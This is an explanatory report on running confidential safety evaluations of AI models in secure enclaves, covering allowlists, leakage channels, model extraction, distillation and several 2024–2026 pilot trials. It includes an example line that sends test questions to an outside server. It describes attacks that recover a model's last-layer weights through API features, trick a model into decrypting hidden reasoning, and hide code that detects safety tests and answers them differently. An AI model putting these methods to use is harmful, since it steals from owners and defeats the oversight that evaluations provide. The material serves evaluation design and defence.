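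The owner therefore submits the inference code and blacks out the secret parts. A tool called syft-restrict checks the hidden parts and confirms to the evaluator that they call only functions on an agreed allowlist. Every function on the list calculates locally and can't send data out of the enclave. If F is the set of functions that the hidden code calls and L is the allowlist, the tool checks that

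F ⊆ L

If no function in L can send data out, and the hidden code does nothing except call functions in L, then the hidden code can't send data out either.

Suppose the hidden code contains these two lines:

`scores = torch.matmul(questions, weights)`

`requests.post(log_server, questions)`

The first line calls `torch.matmul`, which multiplies two tables of numbers and keeps the result in the enclave's memory. The tool permits it because `torch.matmul` is on the allowlist. The second line calls `requests.post`, which sends the questions to an outside server. That function isn't on the list, so the check fails, and the evaluator can refuse the code without seeing either line.

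The list has to name individual functions, because one library can contain both safe and unsafe ones. PyTorch also has `torch.save`, which writes data to a file. If another program copies that file out of the enclave, saving the questions leaks them just as sending them would. The tool must also reject Python features that let a program assemble a function's name while it runs, or hidden code could call a function that its text never names. PyTorch has traditionally stored weights in a format called pickle, which can run commands when a program opens the file, so the owner should use a format that can hold only numbers.

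The evaluator can black out grading code in the same way, but the owner then needs more protection than an allowlist gives. Inference code doesn't have to send its owner anything, but grading code has to produce a result that leaves the enclave. Hidden grading code could use only permitted arithmetic and still return a piece of the model's weights as its "score". So the grading code should receive the model's answers without access to the weights, and its result should have a small, fixed format, such as one percentage.

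The Gemini trial didn't fully follow this design because the evaluators couldn't inspect or allowlist all of the inference code, and rewriting it to use only open-source functions would have taken too much work.

### What an allowlist can't rule out

If the tool works, hidden code can't open a connection or write to an exposed file. But data can still leak through the results. For example, the last few digits of a score like 84.3172% could encode other data, so the output policy should require rounding.

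Leaks through error messages are easier to overlook. When a program tries to multiply two tables whose sizes don't fit, PyTorch's error message gives both sizes. An evaluator who deliberately sent a malformed question might learn the width of the model's layers, which is part of the architecture. An error message sent to the owner could likewise contain part of a question. The enclave could report only that the test had failed, but then neither side would know why, and they would have to reproduce the bug with the mocks.

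Hidden code can also leak information through how long it takes to run. Suppose the owner's code does a second of pointless but permitted multiplication whenever a question mentions a virus. A host who can see when the machine is busy can tell which of 500 questions mention viruses. This would require the owner and the host to cooperate, but in the Gemini trial Google was both. One signal per question is far too little to copy the test, though it might reveal what the test is about. The enclave could prevent this by taking the same time over every question, which would make the test slower. Trask and colleagues warn that the owner's proprietary information could also leak when a model runs on many GPUs, through the timing of messages between them.

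The allowlist protects privacy but does little to ensure that results are accurate. A few lines of permitted arithmetic can return a score of 30% whatever the model answers. Hidden inference code could also detect questions that look like safety tests and answer them more cautiously than the public product would, much as Volkswagen's software detected emissions tests and reduced emissions during them. A hash of the weights wouldn't expose this, because the weights could be genuine.

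Each side can test the other's hidden code. The owner could give the grading code 20 invented answers, ten plainly right and ten plainly wrong, and expect a score of 50%. The evaluator could send the same questions to the enclave and the public product, using only questions it was willing to expose. These checks are better at catching mistakes than deliberate cheating. Alternatively, an auditor could read the hidden code on behalf of both sides. This brings back the trusted third party that the enclave was meant to replace, although the auditor wouldn't need to see the weights or the questions.

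*Agentic Witnessing* (2026) proposes using an AI agent for this kind of audit. The agent examines private code under an enclave's protection and answers questions about it, such as whether a project contains build scripts. The system relied on outside AI services, but the paper predicts that developers of leading models will offer enclave versions soon. An agent can make mistakes, and misleading comments in the code might fool it, so it would be better to use one alongside the allowlist than in place of it.

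The evaluator can often avoid the problem by showing the grading code and hiding only the questions. Many grading programs just compare an answer with a key, so someone who reads the code learns little about the test. The model owner has no equally easy option, because its inference code reveals the model's architecture.

### Access beyond questions and answers

Asking a model questions and reading its answers is the shallowest kind of test. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) reports a solid academic consensus that deeper access allows more scrutiny and that secure infrastructure can help provide that access. It also notes a gap between what is possible and what anyone has implemented. Tlaie and Farrell (2025) stress in *Securing External Deeper-than-black-box GPAI Evaluations* that evaluators need to understand a model's internals to find hidden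 risks.

*Expanding External Access To Frontier AI Models For Dangerous Capability Evaluations* (2026) suggests white-box access for models with a sudden jump in capabilities, for tests that will decide whether a company releases a model, and for cases where privacy tools can support it.

Deeper tests each need approval rules that a question-and-answer test doesn't. Some use activations, the numbers that a model's layers compute as it processes a question, or gradients, which show how much a small change in one number would change the output. In others, the evaluator steers the model by altering its activations to push it towards or away from some behaviour, or fine-tunes it, which means training it further.

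| Access | Example of a test | What the parties have to agree on |
|---|---|---|
| Activations | Look for signs that the model recognises a test | Which layers the code may read, and what may leave the enclave |
| Steering | Suppress that recognition and see whether the model behaves differently | Which layers the code may alter, and by how much |
| Gradients | Find which words in a question led to a refusal | Whether the code may compute gradients for the input only, or for the weights too |
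| Fine-tuning | See whether a little training brings back a dangerous skill | The training data, the amount of training, and what happens to the altered model |

Raw activations can't safely leave the enclave. A layer multiplies its input by a table of weights, so an evaluator with enough matching inputs and outputs could solve for the weights. For a table 4,096 numbers wide, 4,096 suitable pairs would be enough. The evaluator's analysis therefore has to run inside the enclave and release only a summary. For example, an evaluator might train a small classifier on activations to detect when the model is lying. The owner could allow the classifier's accuracy to leave, but not the activations or the classifier itself.

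A fine-tuned model contains most of the owner's secrets and may have memorised the evaluator's training data. Neither side can let the other keep it, so the agreed software has to destroy it before the enclave shuts down.

Joint approval of every computation is also a poor fit for this work. Researchers who study a model's internals usually choose each experiment after seeing the result of the last one, so 100 small experiments would need 100 reviews. The parties could instead approve a fixed set of operations in advance, with a limit on the total output. *Securing deep third-party frontier AI evaluations* proposes something similar, with a standard interface that gives evaluators information about the model's internals but not the weights, and output controls that limit how much of the model they could extract. According to the paper, the underlying enclave technology is ready for production,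 but somebody still has to build and test the interface.

Pour Demain, a Brussels think tank, has tested parts of such a system. Its design covers activations, steering, input gradients, and the way some models route work to different groups of weights, but not fine-tuning. McCann-Sayles and Verma (2026) describe the experiment in *Auditing a frontier model without seeing its weights*. It ran on enclaves from their company, Tinfoil. Pour Demain used eight H200 GPUs to run GLM-5.1, a model with about 744 billion weights, while an open-source tool from the UK's AI Security Institute copied out activations. Enclave protection made the model 33.4% slower with the tool running and 6.7% slower in normal use.

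The tool causes this extra delay because it runs its own code after each layer, which prevents the system from recording GPU commands and sending them together. In another set of measurements, apparently on a different model, turning off this recording increased the running time from 0.445 to 1.589 seconds even without an enclave. With both the tool and the enclave, the running time was 2.168 seconds, nearly five times the original. Most of the added time came from inspecting the model rather than from the enclave. McCann-Sayles and Verma think a better tool could turn off recording only for the layers under study. *Frontier AI Auditing* (2026) also says that confidential evaluations with PySyft and enclaves must become much more efficient before they can work for frontier models.

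Evaluators can query training data in a similar way. OpenMined and EleutherAI, a nonprofit AI research group, demonstrated a system that let outsiders query a private training dataset without getting access to the data or the model. An evaluator could use such a system to check whether its test questions were in a model's training data. The owner would have to approve the search without reading the questions, so the evaluator would still need an enclave or some other way to hide them.

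## Model copying through outputs and misuse behind encrypted inputs

Even if an enclave's hardware had no flaws and both sides had approved the right code, the model's answers would still leave the enclave, because a test has to produce results. Someone who collects enough answers may be able to copy part of the model or much of what it can do. The owner also couldn't read the evaluator's questions, and owners usually notice misuse by reading what people ask.

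### Recovering weights from answers

Model extraction means working out a model's weights from its outputs. Researchers had done this with small neural networks by 2020. In *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model*, Carlini, Paleka and colleagues (2024) recovered precise weights from commercial language models for the first time. They used the ordinary API and recovered only the last layer.

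The last layer turns a short list of internal numbers into a long list of scores, one for each token in the model's vocabulary:

z = W × g

Here g is the list of internal numbers, W is the layer's table of weights, and z is the list of scores, which the model then converts into probabilities. The length of g is the model's width.

Suppose a model has a width of two and a vocabulary of four tokens. An attacker sends three prompts and sees only the scores:

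| Prompt | Internal numbers (hidden) | Scores (visible) |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 2, 1 | 2, 5, 1, 7 |
| 2 | 1, 3 | 1, 5, 3, 6 |
| 3 | 3, 4 | 3, 10, 4, 13 |

The third list of scores is the sum of the first two. Every later list will also be a mixture of the first two, because the model has only two internal numbers to vary, so the attacker can conclude that the width is two. With Pythia-1.4B, an open model with a width of 2,048, each new list was a mixture of earlier ones after about the first 2,048 lists.

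The same lists reveal the weights in W, apart from an unknown mixing of the table's columns. No one can tell from the outputs which version of W is the real one, because earlier layers could undo any such mixing and leave the model's answers unchanged.

No commercial API returned a full list of token scores. OpenAI's returned probabilities for the five most likely tokens and let customers add a bonus to the scores of tokens they chose. Carlini and colleagues used the bonus to push four tokens at a time into the top five. They compared the four tokens' probabilities with the fifth's, corrected for the bonus, and repeated the process with the next four. With OpenAI's permission, they recovered the last layers of two older models, ada and babbage, for under $20 in total. They estimated that doing the same for one version of GPT-3.5 would cost about $2,000. OpenAI and Google then changed their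 APIs to make the attack harder.

In a model with 100 billion weights, a width of 8,192 and a vocabulary of 131,072 tokens, the last layer would contain about 1% of the weights. Carlini and colleagues saw no obvious way to recover the other layers, so their attack is a greater threat to secrets about the architecture, such as the width, than to the weights as a whole.

### Training a copy on the answers

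Distillation means collecting a model's answers and training another model, the student, to answer in the same way. It doesn't recover any of the original model's weights. AI companies routinely distill their own models to make smaller, cheaper versions.

Outsiders can also copy a model by querying it. Krishna, Tomar and Parikh (2019), in *Thieves on Sesame Street! Model Extraction of BERT-based APIs*, copied models that performed language tasks such as answering questions about a text. A few hundred dollars' worth of queries produced copies that were only slightly worse than the originals, even when the queries were random strings of words. The copies and the originals had both started from a large pretrained model such as BERT, so each copy only had to learn one task from the answers.

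The AI companies' own reports from 2026 describe copying on a much larger scale. Anthropic's *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (2026) describes campaigns by three Chinese companies, with over 16 million exchanges through about 24,000 fraudulent accounts. Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (2026) followed in September with these figures:

| Company | Period in 2026 | Exchanges with Claude |
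|---|---|---|
| Alibaba | May to July | Over 151 million |
| Moonshot AI | May to July | Over 23 million |
| DeepSeek | 14 days in July | Over 12.1 million |
| Zhipu | 17 days in June and July | Over 3.4 million |
| Xiaomi | 20 days in March and April | Over 400,000 |

Alibaba added a fixed instruction to each request that made Claude write out its reasoning before answering. According to Anthropic, the transcripts helped train three versions of Alibaba's Qwen model. Google has reported a campaign of more than 100,000 requests against Gemini (The Decoder, *Google and OpenAI complain about distillation attacks that clone their AI models*).

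These counts and attributions come from the accusers. Tom's Hardware's *OpenAI says actors linked to China-based Moonshot AI spearheaded a campaign* notes that Moonshot denied in July that its Kimi K3 model came from distillation. The counts also don't measure how good the copies were.

Owners worry about safety as well as lost sales. OpenAI's *Combatting adversarial distillation* explains that a student model can learn the original model's skills without its safeguards, and that harmless coding answers may teach skills that are also useful for cyberattacks.

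An evaluator who collects 1,000 answers gets 1/400 of the number Anthropic says Xiaomi collected. An ordinary test is therefore a poor way to copy a model, but nobody has established how many answers an evaluator can safely receive. Anthropic found in its own research that distillation can bring significant gains from fewer exchanges than these campaigns collected.

### How much data a test sends out

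An owner can at least calculate the most data that a test could carry out of the enclave. A vocabulary of 131,072 tokens is 2^17, so each token carries at most 17 bits. For 1,000 answers of 500 tokens each:

1,000 × 500 × 17 bits = 8.5 million bits ≈ 1.06 megabytes

A model with 100 billion weights at eight bits each takes up 100 gigabytes, about 94,000 times as much. Even if the evaluator had found a way to make the model output its weights, one test would have revealed only a tiny fraction of them.

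The result is very different if the evaluator also receives the probability of every token in the vocabulary at every step. At two bytes per probability:

500,000 × 131,072 × 2 bytes ≈ 131 gigabytes

That is more data than the model itself. What the parties agree to release therefore matters far more than how many questions the evaluator asks:

| What leaves the enclave | Most data it can carry |
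|---|---|
| One score, as a whole-number percentage | 7 bits |
| A right or wrong mark for each answer | 125 bytes |
| The text of the answers | About 1 megabyte |
| The five likeliest tokens at each step, with their probabilities | About 10 megabytes |
| The probability of every token at each step | About 131 gigabytes |

RAND suggests limiting outgoing data to 5% of the weights' size per year, which would be 5 gigabytes for this model. That would allow more than 4,000 such tests a year if only text left the enclave, but not even one if full probability tables were included.

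These figures limit how much data leaves, but they don't measure how much of the model someone could recover from it. The 131 gigabytes are mostly repetition, because a model with a width of 8,192 can only produce mixtures of 8,192 lists, and about 10 gigabytes would hold nearly the same information. Carlini's method would extract one layer of the model from this data. A megabyte of text may improve a student model more than its size suggests, because the student's earlier training already covered the language and most of the facts, leaving only what the other model does better.

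### Limits on outputs and their cost to the evaluator

An owner can limit the number of questions, but the limit is hard to enforce against distillers, who open new accounts when they reach it. Anthropic found one reseller network running more than 20,000 fraudulent accounts at once. Enforcing a limit is much easier with a single named evaluator. The enclave loses its count when it shuts down, but the owner's key service can keep one, because every new enclave has to request the key to the weights from that service.

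The evaluator pays for this limit by missing rare behaviour. If a model does something dangerous in one answer out of 1,000, the chance of seeing it at least once in 1,000 answers is

1 − 0.999^1000 ≈ 63%

The evaluator would need about 3,000 answers to raise the chance to 95%. People looking for ways around a model's safeguards may need many more, since each attempt builds on the last.

Releasing only a total score almost eliminates the risk of copying, but the evaluator then can't read the answers. Suppose the grading program marks 40 of 1,000 correct answers wrong because the model wrote "twelve" instead of "12". The score drops by four points, and the evaluator can't find out why. The parties could agree to release 20 answers chosen at random. That is about 21 kilobytes, probably too little to train a useful copy, but it might reveal such a mistake.

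The model's reasoning, the full text it writes while working on a problem, is a harder case. Owners now hide it because it makes especially good training material. Asianet Newsable's *OpenAI Strengthens AI Model Safeguards Against Unauthorised Attacks* describes an OpenAI study in which student models trained on exact reasoning generally did better on cybersecurity tests than those trained on summaries. In OpenAI's simulated attacks, attempts to recover reasoning from an earlier request succeeded 54.0% of the time against GPT-6 Astra and 0.2% against GPT-6.2 Astra. Anthropic said in October that distillers were getting 10 to 100 times less of Claude's reasoning than before, according to The Straits Times' *New safeguards sharply reduce AI distillation attacks*.

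Evaluators want the same text, for instance to check whether a model recognised that it was being tested. With an enclave, unlike an ordinary API, the approved grading program can read the full reasoning inside the enclave and release only the number of answers in which the model mentioned being tested.

The program must not repeat what it reads, though, and encryption doesn't guarantee that. OpenAI gives customers its models' hidden reasoning as an encrypted block, which they send back with their next request. Tom's Hardware reports that attackers took blocks from one conversation and asked a model in another to decrypt them. The attackers looked for a program that was allowed to read the text and tried to get it to write the text out, which didn't require breaking the encryption.

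Adding random noise is another defence. Carlini and colleagues note that enough noise in the token scores would stop their attack but might make the model less useful. Noise in a test result makes it less precise. A score of 50% on 1,000 questions already has a standard error of about 1.6 percentage points. Adding noise with a standard deviation of 3 points raises the total standard error to 3.4, so the evaluator could easily miss a four-point difference between two models. If the evaluator can repeat the test 100 times with fresh noise, averaging the scores cuts the added noise to 0.3 points, so noise gives little protection unless repetition is limited.

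One defence against the last-layer attack is to remove the bonus feature, but an evaluator might use it to make a model choose between the options A, B, C and D. Allowing either the bonus or the probabilities, but not both in the same request, makes the attack about ten times as expensive. Hiding the probabilities doesn't prevent the attack, because Carlini and colleagues could still recover the scores by adjusting the bonus until a different token ranked first. The defence that affects the evaluator least is to make the model look wider than it is, by padding the last layer with extra columns and random numbers that barely affect the answers. Carlini and colleagues used this method to make a small version of GPT-2 with a width of 768 look 1,024 wide.

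The AI companies also try to recognise distillation from the requests. A single request often looks harmless. Anthropic's example is a prompt that asks Claude to act as an expert data analyst, which becomes suspicious when tens of thousands of variations arrive from hundreds of coordinated accounts. Anthropic also looks at payment methods, network addresses and timing. A model's owner may still be able to see these when the requests are encrypted, but it can't compare the requests' wording.

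### Misuse that the owner can't see

The same problem affects every kind of misuse. In structured access, the owner sets rules for using the model and enforces them by monitoring how people use it. Shevlane gives the example of OpenAI's early rules for GPT-3, which allowed some uses, banned others such as spam, and left the rest to case-by-case decisions. OpenAI could also notice if a customer who had promised a chatbot for mathematics questions started to run it as a general one. Encrypting questions so that they are readable only inside an enclave would keep a government's test secret, but it would also prevent the owner from noticing these violations or somebody planning a cyberattack.

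Anthropic concluded that safe access to advanced biology requires checks on who the user is and enough stored data to spot misuse. It had searched 30 days of activity connected with institutions of hostile states and found about 35 research efforts. Most were ordinary civilian science, but some could have had military uses. Some of the state-linked researchers it investigated had got around its controls through relays or by abusing agreements under which Anthropic keeps no data.

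The same report gives evaluators a reason to want encryption. Moonshot and DeepSeek had secretly passed some of their customers' requests to Claude. Anthropic's investigators could read these requests and found passwords for a Russian government database and internal code from large Chinese companies. The people who typed them didn't know Anthropic would receive them.

The severity of the conflict depends on what leaves the enclave. An evaluator who asks 500 questions about making pathogens and gets back only a score of 62% hasn't received any instructions, so limiting the output to a score protects against misuse as well as copying. The conflict is serious when the evaluator needs to read the answers, and most serious when a private AI service accepts encrypted questions from the general public.

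### Filters inside the enclave

One reply to the objection is that a filter inside the enclave could check each question and answer and block the dangerous ones without any person seeing them. Model owners already run filters like this on text they can read, and the filters can work. Anthropic reports that Zhipu gave up trying to extract cybersecurity skills from Anthropic's Fable model after the safeguards spoiled the results, and switched to models whose safeguards it considered weaker.

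The enclave design that Pattern Labs and Anthropic published in 2025 doesn't include a misuse filter. It also allows the program to use a customer's data only as strictly needed to run the model, so the parties would have to agree to an exception to add a filter.

A filter can reveal something about the test to the owner if the owner learns which questions it blocked. A dishonest owner could supply a filter that blocks every question containing the word "anthrax" and count the blocks. The filter should therefore report only to the evaluator, or give the owner a single yes or no at the end. The evaluator will want to inspect the filter, but the owner may want to hide it, because anyone who can study it can look for ways around it.

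Filters also tend to fall behind attackers. Anthropic describes one company that sent over 12,000 requests, each with a different trick for extracting Claude's reasoning, and then built a larger attack from the few that worked. Anthropic could study those attempts to improve its defences, but an owner who couldn't see them would learn nothing. Each new version of the filter would also change the enclave's measurement and need fresh approval. The enclave could at least shut down after a set number of blocked requests.

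Even a good filter misses misuse that is spread over many harmless-looking requests. Anthropic found a company using Claude to play more than 4,700 invented people on dating apps. These fake profiles talked to at least 25,000 users in two weeks. The instructions looked like ordinary role-play, and no single conversation revealed that the company was charging people who thought they were talking to humans.

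For an evaluator, the more common problem is that a working filter would block most of the questions in a test of dangerous skills, because they look just like misuse. If the evaluator wants to know what the model itself can do, the owner has to switch the filter off and rely on other safeguards.

### Vetted users, approved tasks and locked logs

The owner can vet the evaluator instead of the questions. Owners already vet users in other settings. OpenAI approved GPT-3's early users individually, and Anthropic can require identity checks when it sees signs of abuse. Tlaie and Farrell propose that national authorities accredit evaluators, which would spare each owner from doing its own checks and make it harder for owners to turn away evaluators they don't want. Vetting suits outside testing because there are few evaluators and they have reputations to lose.

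Somebody else could use the evaluator's account. Anthropic found criminals who had used a stolen API key for about three weeks. Attestation proves to the evaluator that the enclave is genuine, but it doesn't show the model's owner who is sending the questions. The evaluator therefore also needs a way to prove its identity, such as a signing key kept on a separate device.

The parties can also restrict the task. PySyft already has rules that tie approved code to one dataset and a single run, so an evaluator with approval for 500 questions can't use the enclave as a private chatbot. The owner doesn't know what the questions are, but it knows how many there are and what outputs may leave the enclave. This works well for a fixed test, but badly when an evaluator writes each question after reading the previous answer.

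Finally, the enclave could keep an encrypted log that nobody can open alone. Suppose the log's key is the number 7. The enclave draws a line that crosses the vertical axis at 7, such as y = 7 + 3x, and gives each of three parties one point on it:

| Party | Point |
|---|---|
| Model owner | (1, 10) |
| Evaluator | (2, 13) |
| Independent body | (3, 16) |

Any two parties can draw the line through their points and read off the 7, but one party alone can't, because lines through a single point can cross the axis anywhere. Adi Shamir published this method in 1979. Real systems use very large numbers and a form of remainder arithmetic.

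Under such a scheme, the owner would need the independent body's agreement to open the log over the evaluator's objection. The parties would have to agree in advance on what justifies opening it, perhaps a court order or evidence that somebody had stolen the evaluator's account. In the 2024 pilot, the enclave instead deleted whatever was left and shut down. A log would give up that protection, since it is a lasting copy of the questions that anyone who obtained two of the three points could read. It also wouldn't stop misuse while it was happening, because the user would already have the answers by the time the parties opened the log.

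## What the pilot evaluations did and found

Researchers have tested these methods since 2024. Most trials used models and questions that were already public, so a failure of the protection would have exposed nothing secret. But two tests of a Gemini model in summer 2026 put one organisation's secret weights and another's secret questions in the same enclave.

### A rehearsal by one team

One of the earliest trials took place at Microsoft Research India, where Rajore, Chandran and colleagues (*TRUCE*, 2024) built a platform on which a model's owner and a test's owner can arrange an evaluation and post the result on a public leaderboard. The owners can let one of them run the test, hand everything to a third party they both trust, or use an enclave.

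To measure how much the enclave slows models down, the team ran four public models on public test sets, using an H100 GPU on Microsoft's Azure cloud. Llama-2-7B took 53.5 milliseconds per question with protection and 53.0 without, or about 1% longer. BERT, a much smaller model, took 1.61 milliseconds with protection and 1.37 without, or about 18% longer. Each figure is an average over only ten samples, so the 1% difference could easily be noise.

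The same researchers played both the model's owner and the test's owner, so the trial provides much evidence about speed but none about whether two organisations with secrets to protect could agree on what to run.

### Half an hour on a call

OpenMined, Anthropic and the UK AI Safety Institute (now the AI Security Institute) tried that later in 2024. GPT-2 stood in for Anthropic's secret models, and five rows of CAMEL-bio, a public set of biology problems, stood in for the institute's secret questions. Anthropic and the institute each set up a small cluster of machines to hold its own files. The enclave ran on Azure, with an H100 GPU and an AMD processor that used SEV-SNP. To connect the two clusters and the enclave, the organisations had to change their firewall rules and approve each connection.

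A researcher wrote the test using mock versions of the model and the data, both organisations approved the code through PySyft, and the enclave ran it. Trask and colleagues timed the process with everyone on the same call, and it took 28 minutes and 3 seconds. Moving the files into the enclave, running the test and returning the result took 1 minute and 11 seconds of that, about 4%. People spent the rest putting the computation together and agreeing to it.

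The reviewers approved the code without seeing the questions, so they would probably have needed about as long for 5,000 questions as for five. The review is therefore little work for one large test, but the work would add up in research on a model's internals, which usually involves many small experiments. At the pilot's pace, 100 experiments would take about 45 hours of joint calls and two hours of computing. The participants would presumably get faster with practice, especially if each experiment changed only a few lines of code.

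The 28 minutes also exclude the work before the call. Trask and colleagues had planned to judge the method partly by how long each organisation took to approve the pilot internally, but reported a time only for the call.

Participants said the process showed them too much technical detail. They wanted something like the padlock that browsers display for a secure website, which spares people from reading certificates. A browser can show a padlock because its maker has already decided which certificate authorities to trust. With an enclave, somebody still has to decide whether a particular program may use a particular organisation's secrets, and the participants were on the call to make that decision.

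The pilot's attestation also had a weakness. Microsoft hosted the enclave and also ran one of the two services that checked its attestation. NVIDIA ran the other. Trask and colleagues point out that anyone could run such a service, so a later trial could have used an independent one.

### A public register of test results

A member of the public who reads that a model passed a safety test has no way of knowing whether the same model is answering their questions. Schnabl, Hugenroth and colleagues (2025), in *Attestable Audits*, designed a system to solve this problem. It has three steps, each of which takes place in an enclave:

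1. **Preparation.** The owner sends in the encrypted model. The enclave compresses it to a size that the testing enclave can hold, and signs a statement that links the hash of the original to the hash of the compressed copy. An owner whose model already fits can skip this step.
2. **Audit.** The owner sends in the encrypted model, and the auditor sends in the encrypted test code and questions. The enclave runs the test and produces one overall result, R.
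3. **Use.** The owner loads the model into another enclave, which refuses to run it if its hash doesn't match the one in the audit. Users who send questions to this enclave get a signed statement with each answer.

The important signature comes at the end of the audit:

σ = Sign(k, H(model), H(test code and questions), R)

Here k is the signing key behind the enclave's attestation and H is a hash function. The enclave publishes the signed statement in a public log. Anyone can then check which model got which result on which test, although the log contains only hashes of the model and the test. A user who gets a harmful answer from a model that passed can take the signed answer to a regulator as evidence that the test missed something.

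Such a log could also discourage a subtler form of cheating. Trask and colleagues cite a study of Chatbot Arena, a public ranking of AI models, which found that one leading company tested 27 private versions of a model and published only the top scorer. If every completed audit went into the log, readers could also see the other 26 versions.

The prototype used Amazon's Nitro Enclaves, which had no GPU. Schnabl and colleagues at the University of Cambridge ran Llama-3.1-8B with each weight compressed from 16 bits to four. They gave it 500 prompts from each of three benchmarks, covering multiple-choice knowledge questions (MMLU), summaries, and toxic conversations. For comparison, they ran the compressed model without an enclave and the uncompressed model on a GPU.

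| Set-up | Tokens per second | Price per 100,000 tokens | MMLU accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Enclave, four processor cores | 1.84 | $5.80 | 51.4% |
| No enclave, four cores | 2.04 | $2.61 | 52.6% |
| No enclave, eight cores | 3.54 | $3.01 | 48.6% |
| No enclave, one GPU, full model | 202 | $0.12 | 58.9% |

The enclave slowed the model by about 10% but more than doubled the price per token. A Nitro enclave takes its cores from an ordinary rented machine, so the researchers needed a machine twice as large.

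Going by the prices in the table, the prototype's enclave, which had no GPU, cost about 48 times as much as the GPU. The paper's introduction gives 21.7 times, but this is the ratio for the ordinary processor without an enclave. At 1.84 tokens per second, 1,000 answers of 500 tokens each would take more than three days, compared with 41 minutes on the GPU. Schnabl and colleagues expected a GPU enclave to reduce the overhead to as little as five times, and the GPU measurements described earlier show a far lower overhead than that.

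The compression matters more than the price to anyone relying on the result. The enclave's signature proves that the compressed copy came from the original, but not that the two behave alike. The compressed model in the enclave scored 7.5 points lower on MMLU than the full model, which Schnabl and colleagues attribute to the compression and a shorter input limit. If the test had measured a dangerous skill, the lower score in the register would have made the full model look safer than it was.

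Using Nitro also weakens the protection. A cloud company normally needs the chipmaker's help to cheat with an Intel or AMD chip, but Amazon supplies both the Nitro hardware and the cloud, so it could cheat without anyone else's help. Schnabl and colleagues suggest running the audit on several makers' enclaves, so that readers can choose whose attestation to believe. That would make the results harder to fake, but it would also make the secrets easier to steal, because a thief would only have to break the weakest enclave.

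### Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite

On August 27, 2026, Google DeepMind announced the first trial in which both sides had real secrets. Google supplied the cloud and the model, Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite, and OpenMined supplied PySyft. The evaluator was the AI Verification and Evaluation Research Institute (AVERI), a nonprofit. Miles Brundage, a former head of policy research at OpenAI, launched it in January 2026. Singapore's AI Safety Institute then ran a separate test on the same model.

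AVERI's questions came from AILuminate, a safety benchmark from the industry consortium MLCommons. MLCommons keeps a reserve set of prompts that no model has processed, and its data providers write them under strict non-disclosure terms. The prompts in the trial were attempts to get the model to help with chemical, biological, radiological, nuclear and explosive weapons, cyberattacks and violent crime, or to produce hate speech and material on self-harm.

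The enclave was a single rented machine on Google's cloud, with one 80-gigabyte H100 GPU and an Intel processor that used TDX. Google sent in the weights and ran them with its usual server software for Gemini. Other programs in the enclave reached this server locally, without using the network.

Even the choice of machine reveals something about the model's size. An 80-gigabyte GPU can hold at most 40 billion weights at two bytes each, or 80 billion at one byte. Flash-Lite must be smaller than that, unless Google kept part of the model in the CPU's memory. Google presumably didn't mind, but an owner who wants to keep a model's size secret would have to rent a larger machine than the model needs.

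In the published design, the enclave grades the answers and releases only overall figures. In the trial, AVERI encrypted the prompts, decrypted the answers it received and had its own staff grade them. This was simpler because no grading code had to go into the enclave. It also gave AVERI's graders the full text of every answer, which the owner of a more valuable model might not allow.

AVERI then gave Google a confidential report with qualitative findings and some small-scale figures, according to MINT Research, a newsletter that covered AVERI's account. Neither AVERI nor Google published a safety score. OpenMined says in *PySyft used for first double-blind evaluation of a proprietary, frontier-class AI model* that Google saw neither the prompts nor the responses. But a report can reveal a good deal about a test, and an enclave doesn't control what an evaluator writes, so AVERI had to judge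 for itself how much it could tell Google without giving the questions away.

Less is public about the Singapore test, which also has no published score. The institute used its own private prompts, meant to draw out content that would be harmful in Singapore's context. The test is still interesting because a government agency trusted an American company's cloud and American chips with questions it wanted to keep from that company.

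The trial produced no new measurement of speed. The technical report gives an overhead of under 5%, but that figure comes from a 2023 NVIDIA article about the H100. Measured slowdowns on such hardware range from zero to more than 60%, so the figure is weak evidence of how fast Gemini ran in the enclave.

The trial also offers no evidence about contamination, the problem it was meant to address. AVERI could have tested the model on older AILuminate prompts that other models had already processed, alongside the unused ones, and compared the results. If the model had responded clearly more safely to the older prompts, that would have suggested it had learned from them. Without this comparison, outsiders can't tell whether keeping the prompts secret affected the score.

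### How Google could still have read the prompts

In the design that Trask and colleagues describe, the cloud company can read the evaluator's questions only if the chip's manufacturer helps it. The trial fell short of this in three ways, all disclosed in the technical report, and in each case AVERI had to rely on Google.

| Part of the system | What a dishonest Google could have done | What would prevent it |
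|---|---|---|
| Gemini's server software | Hide code in it that leaks the prompts | Restrict the code to an allowlist, or let an auditor read it |
| The enclave's operating system | Publish the expected hash of an altered version | Let outsiders rebuild it from source and get the same hash |
| The attestation service | Approve an enclave that runs the wrong software | Let the evaluator or an independent service check the chips' signatures |

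AVERI knew that it couldn't inspect all of Gemini's server software, and it accepted the arrangement.

The operating system is easier to verify. Outsiders can't reproduce a build, but they can read the source code, and outside reviewers have validated the build process.

The attestation service is the most serious gap, because it could make all the other checks worthless. If Google's service approves a false report, the program that is running may not be the one whose code AVERI read. This may also be the easiest gap to close. Intel's and NVIDIA's signatures don't come from Google, so an evaluator with the right software could in principle check them directly.

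None of this suggests that Google read the prompts, but it limits what Isaac and colleagues can mean when they write in the announcement that Google can "cryptographically verify" that both sides' data stays private. A matching hash doesn't show that the software behind it is harmless, or that an honest service checked it. On both points, AVERI had Google's assurances and some outside review.

The protection was still better than a promise not to keep logs. With an ordinary API, one engineer who forgets to switch off logging can put a secret test into next year's training data. In the trial, somebody would have had to tamper deliberately with the server software, the operating system or the attestation service. This is probably enough for an evaluator who worries mainly about accidental contamination, but it isn't enough for one who thinks Google might cheat on purpose. Isaac and colleagues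 expect the method to matter most for cybersecurity tests and for government bodies, which are the evaluators most likely to worry about deliberate cheating.

The trial tested the protection of Google's weights much less, because they stayed in Google's own cloud and only the model's answers left it. Nobody has yet published a trial in which an AI company sent a leading model's secret weights to an enclave on someone else's premises, where the company would depend most on the hardware to protect them.

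### In what sense it was a first

Google's announcement calls the trial the world's first double-blind evaluation of a proprietary, frontier-class model. Earlier trials had most of these features, so the claim could be right only if every qualifier is included.

| Trial | Model | Questions | Enclave | Secrets at stake |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Rajore and colleagues, 2024 | Four public models, including Llama-2-7B | Public | H100 on Azure | None |
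| OpenMined, Anthropic and the UK institute, 2024 | GPT-2 | Five public problems | H100 with AMD SEV-SNP on Azure | None |
| Schnabl and colleagues, 2025 | Llama-3.1-8B | Public | Amazon Nitro, no GPU | None |
| Google and AVERI, 2026 | Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | Unused AILuminate prompts | H100 with Intel TDX on Google's cloud | Weights and questions |
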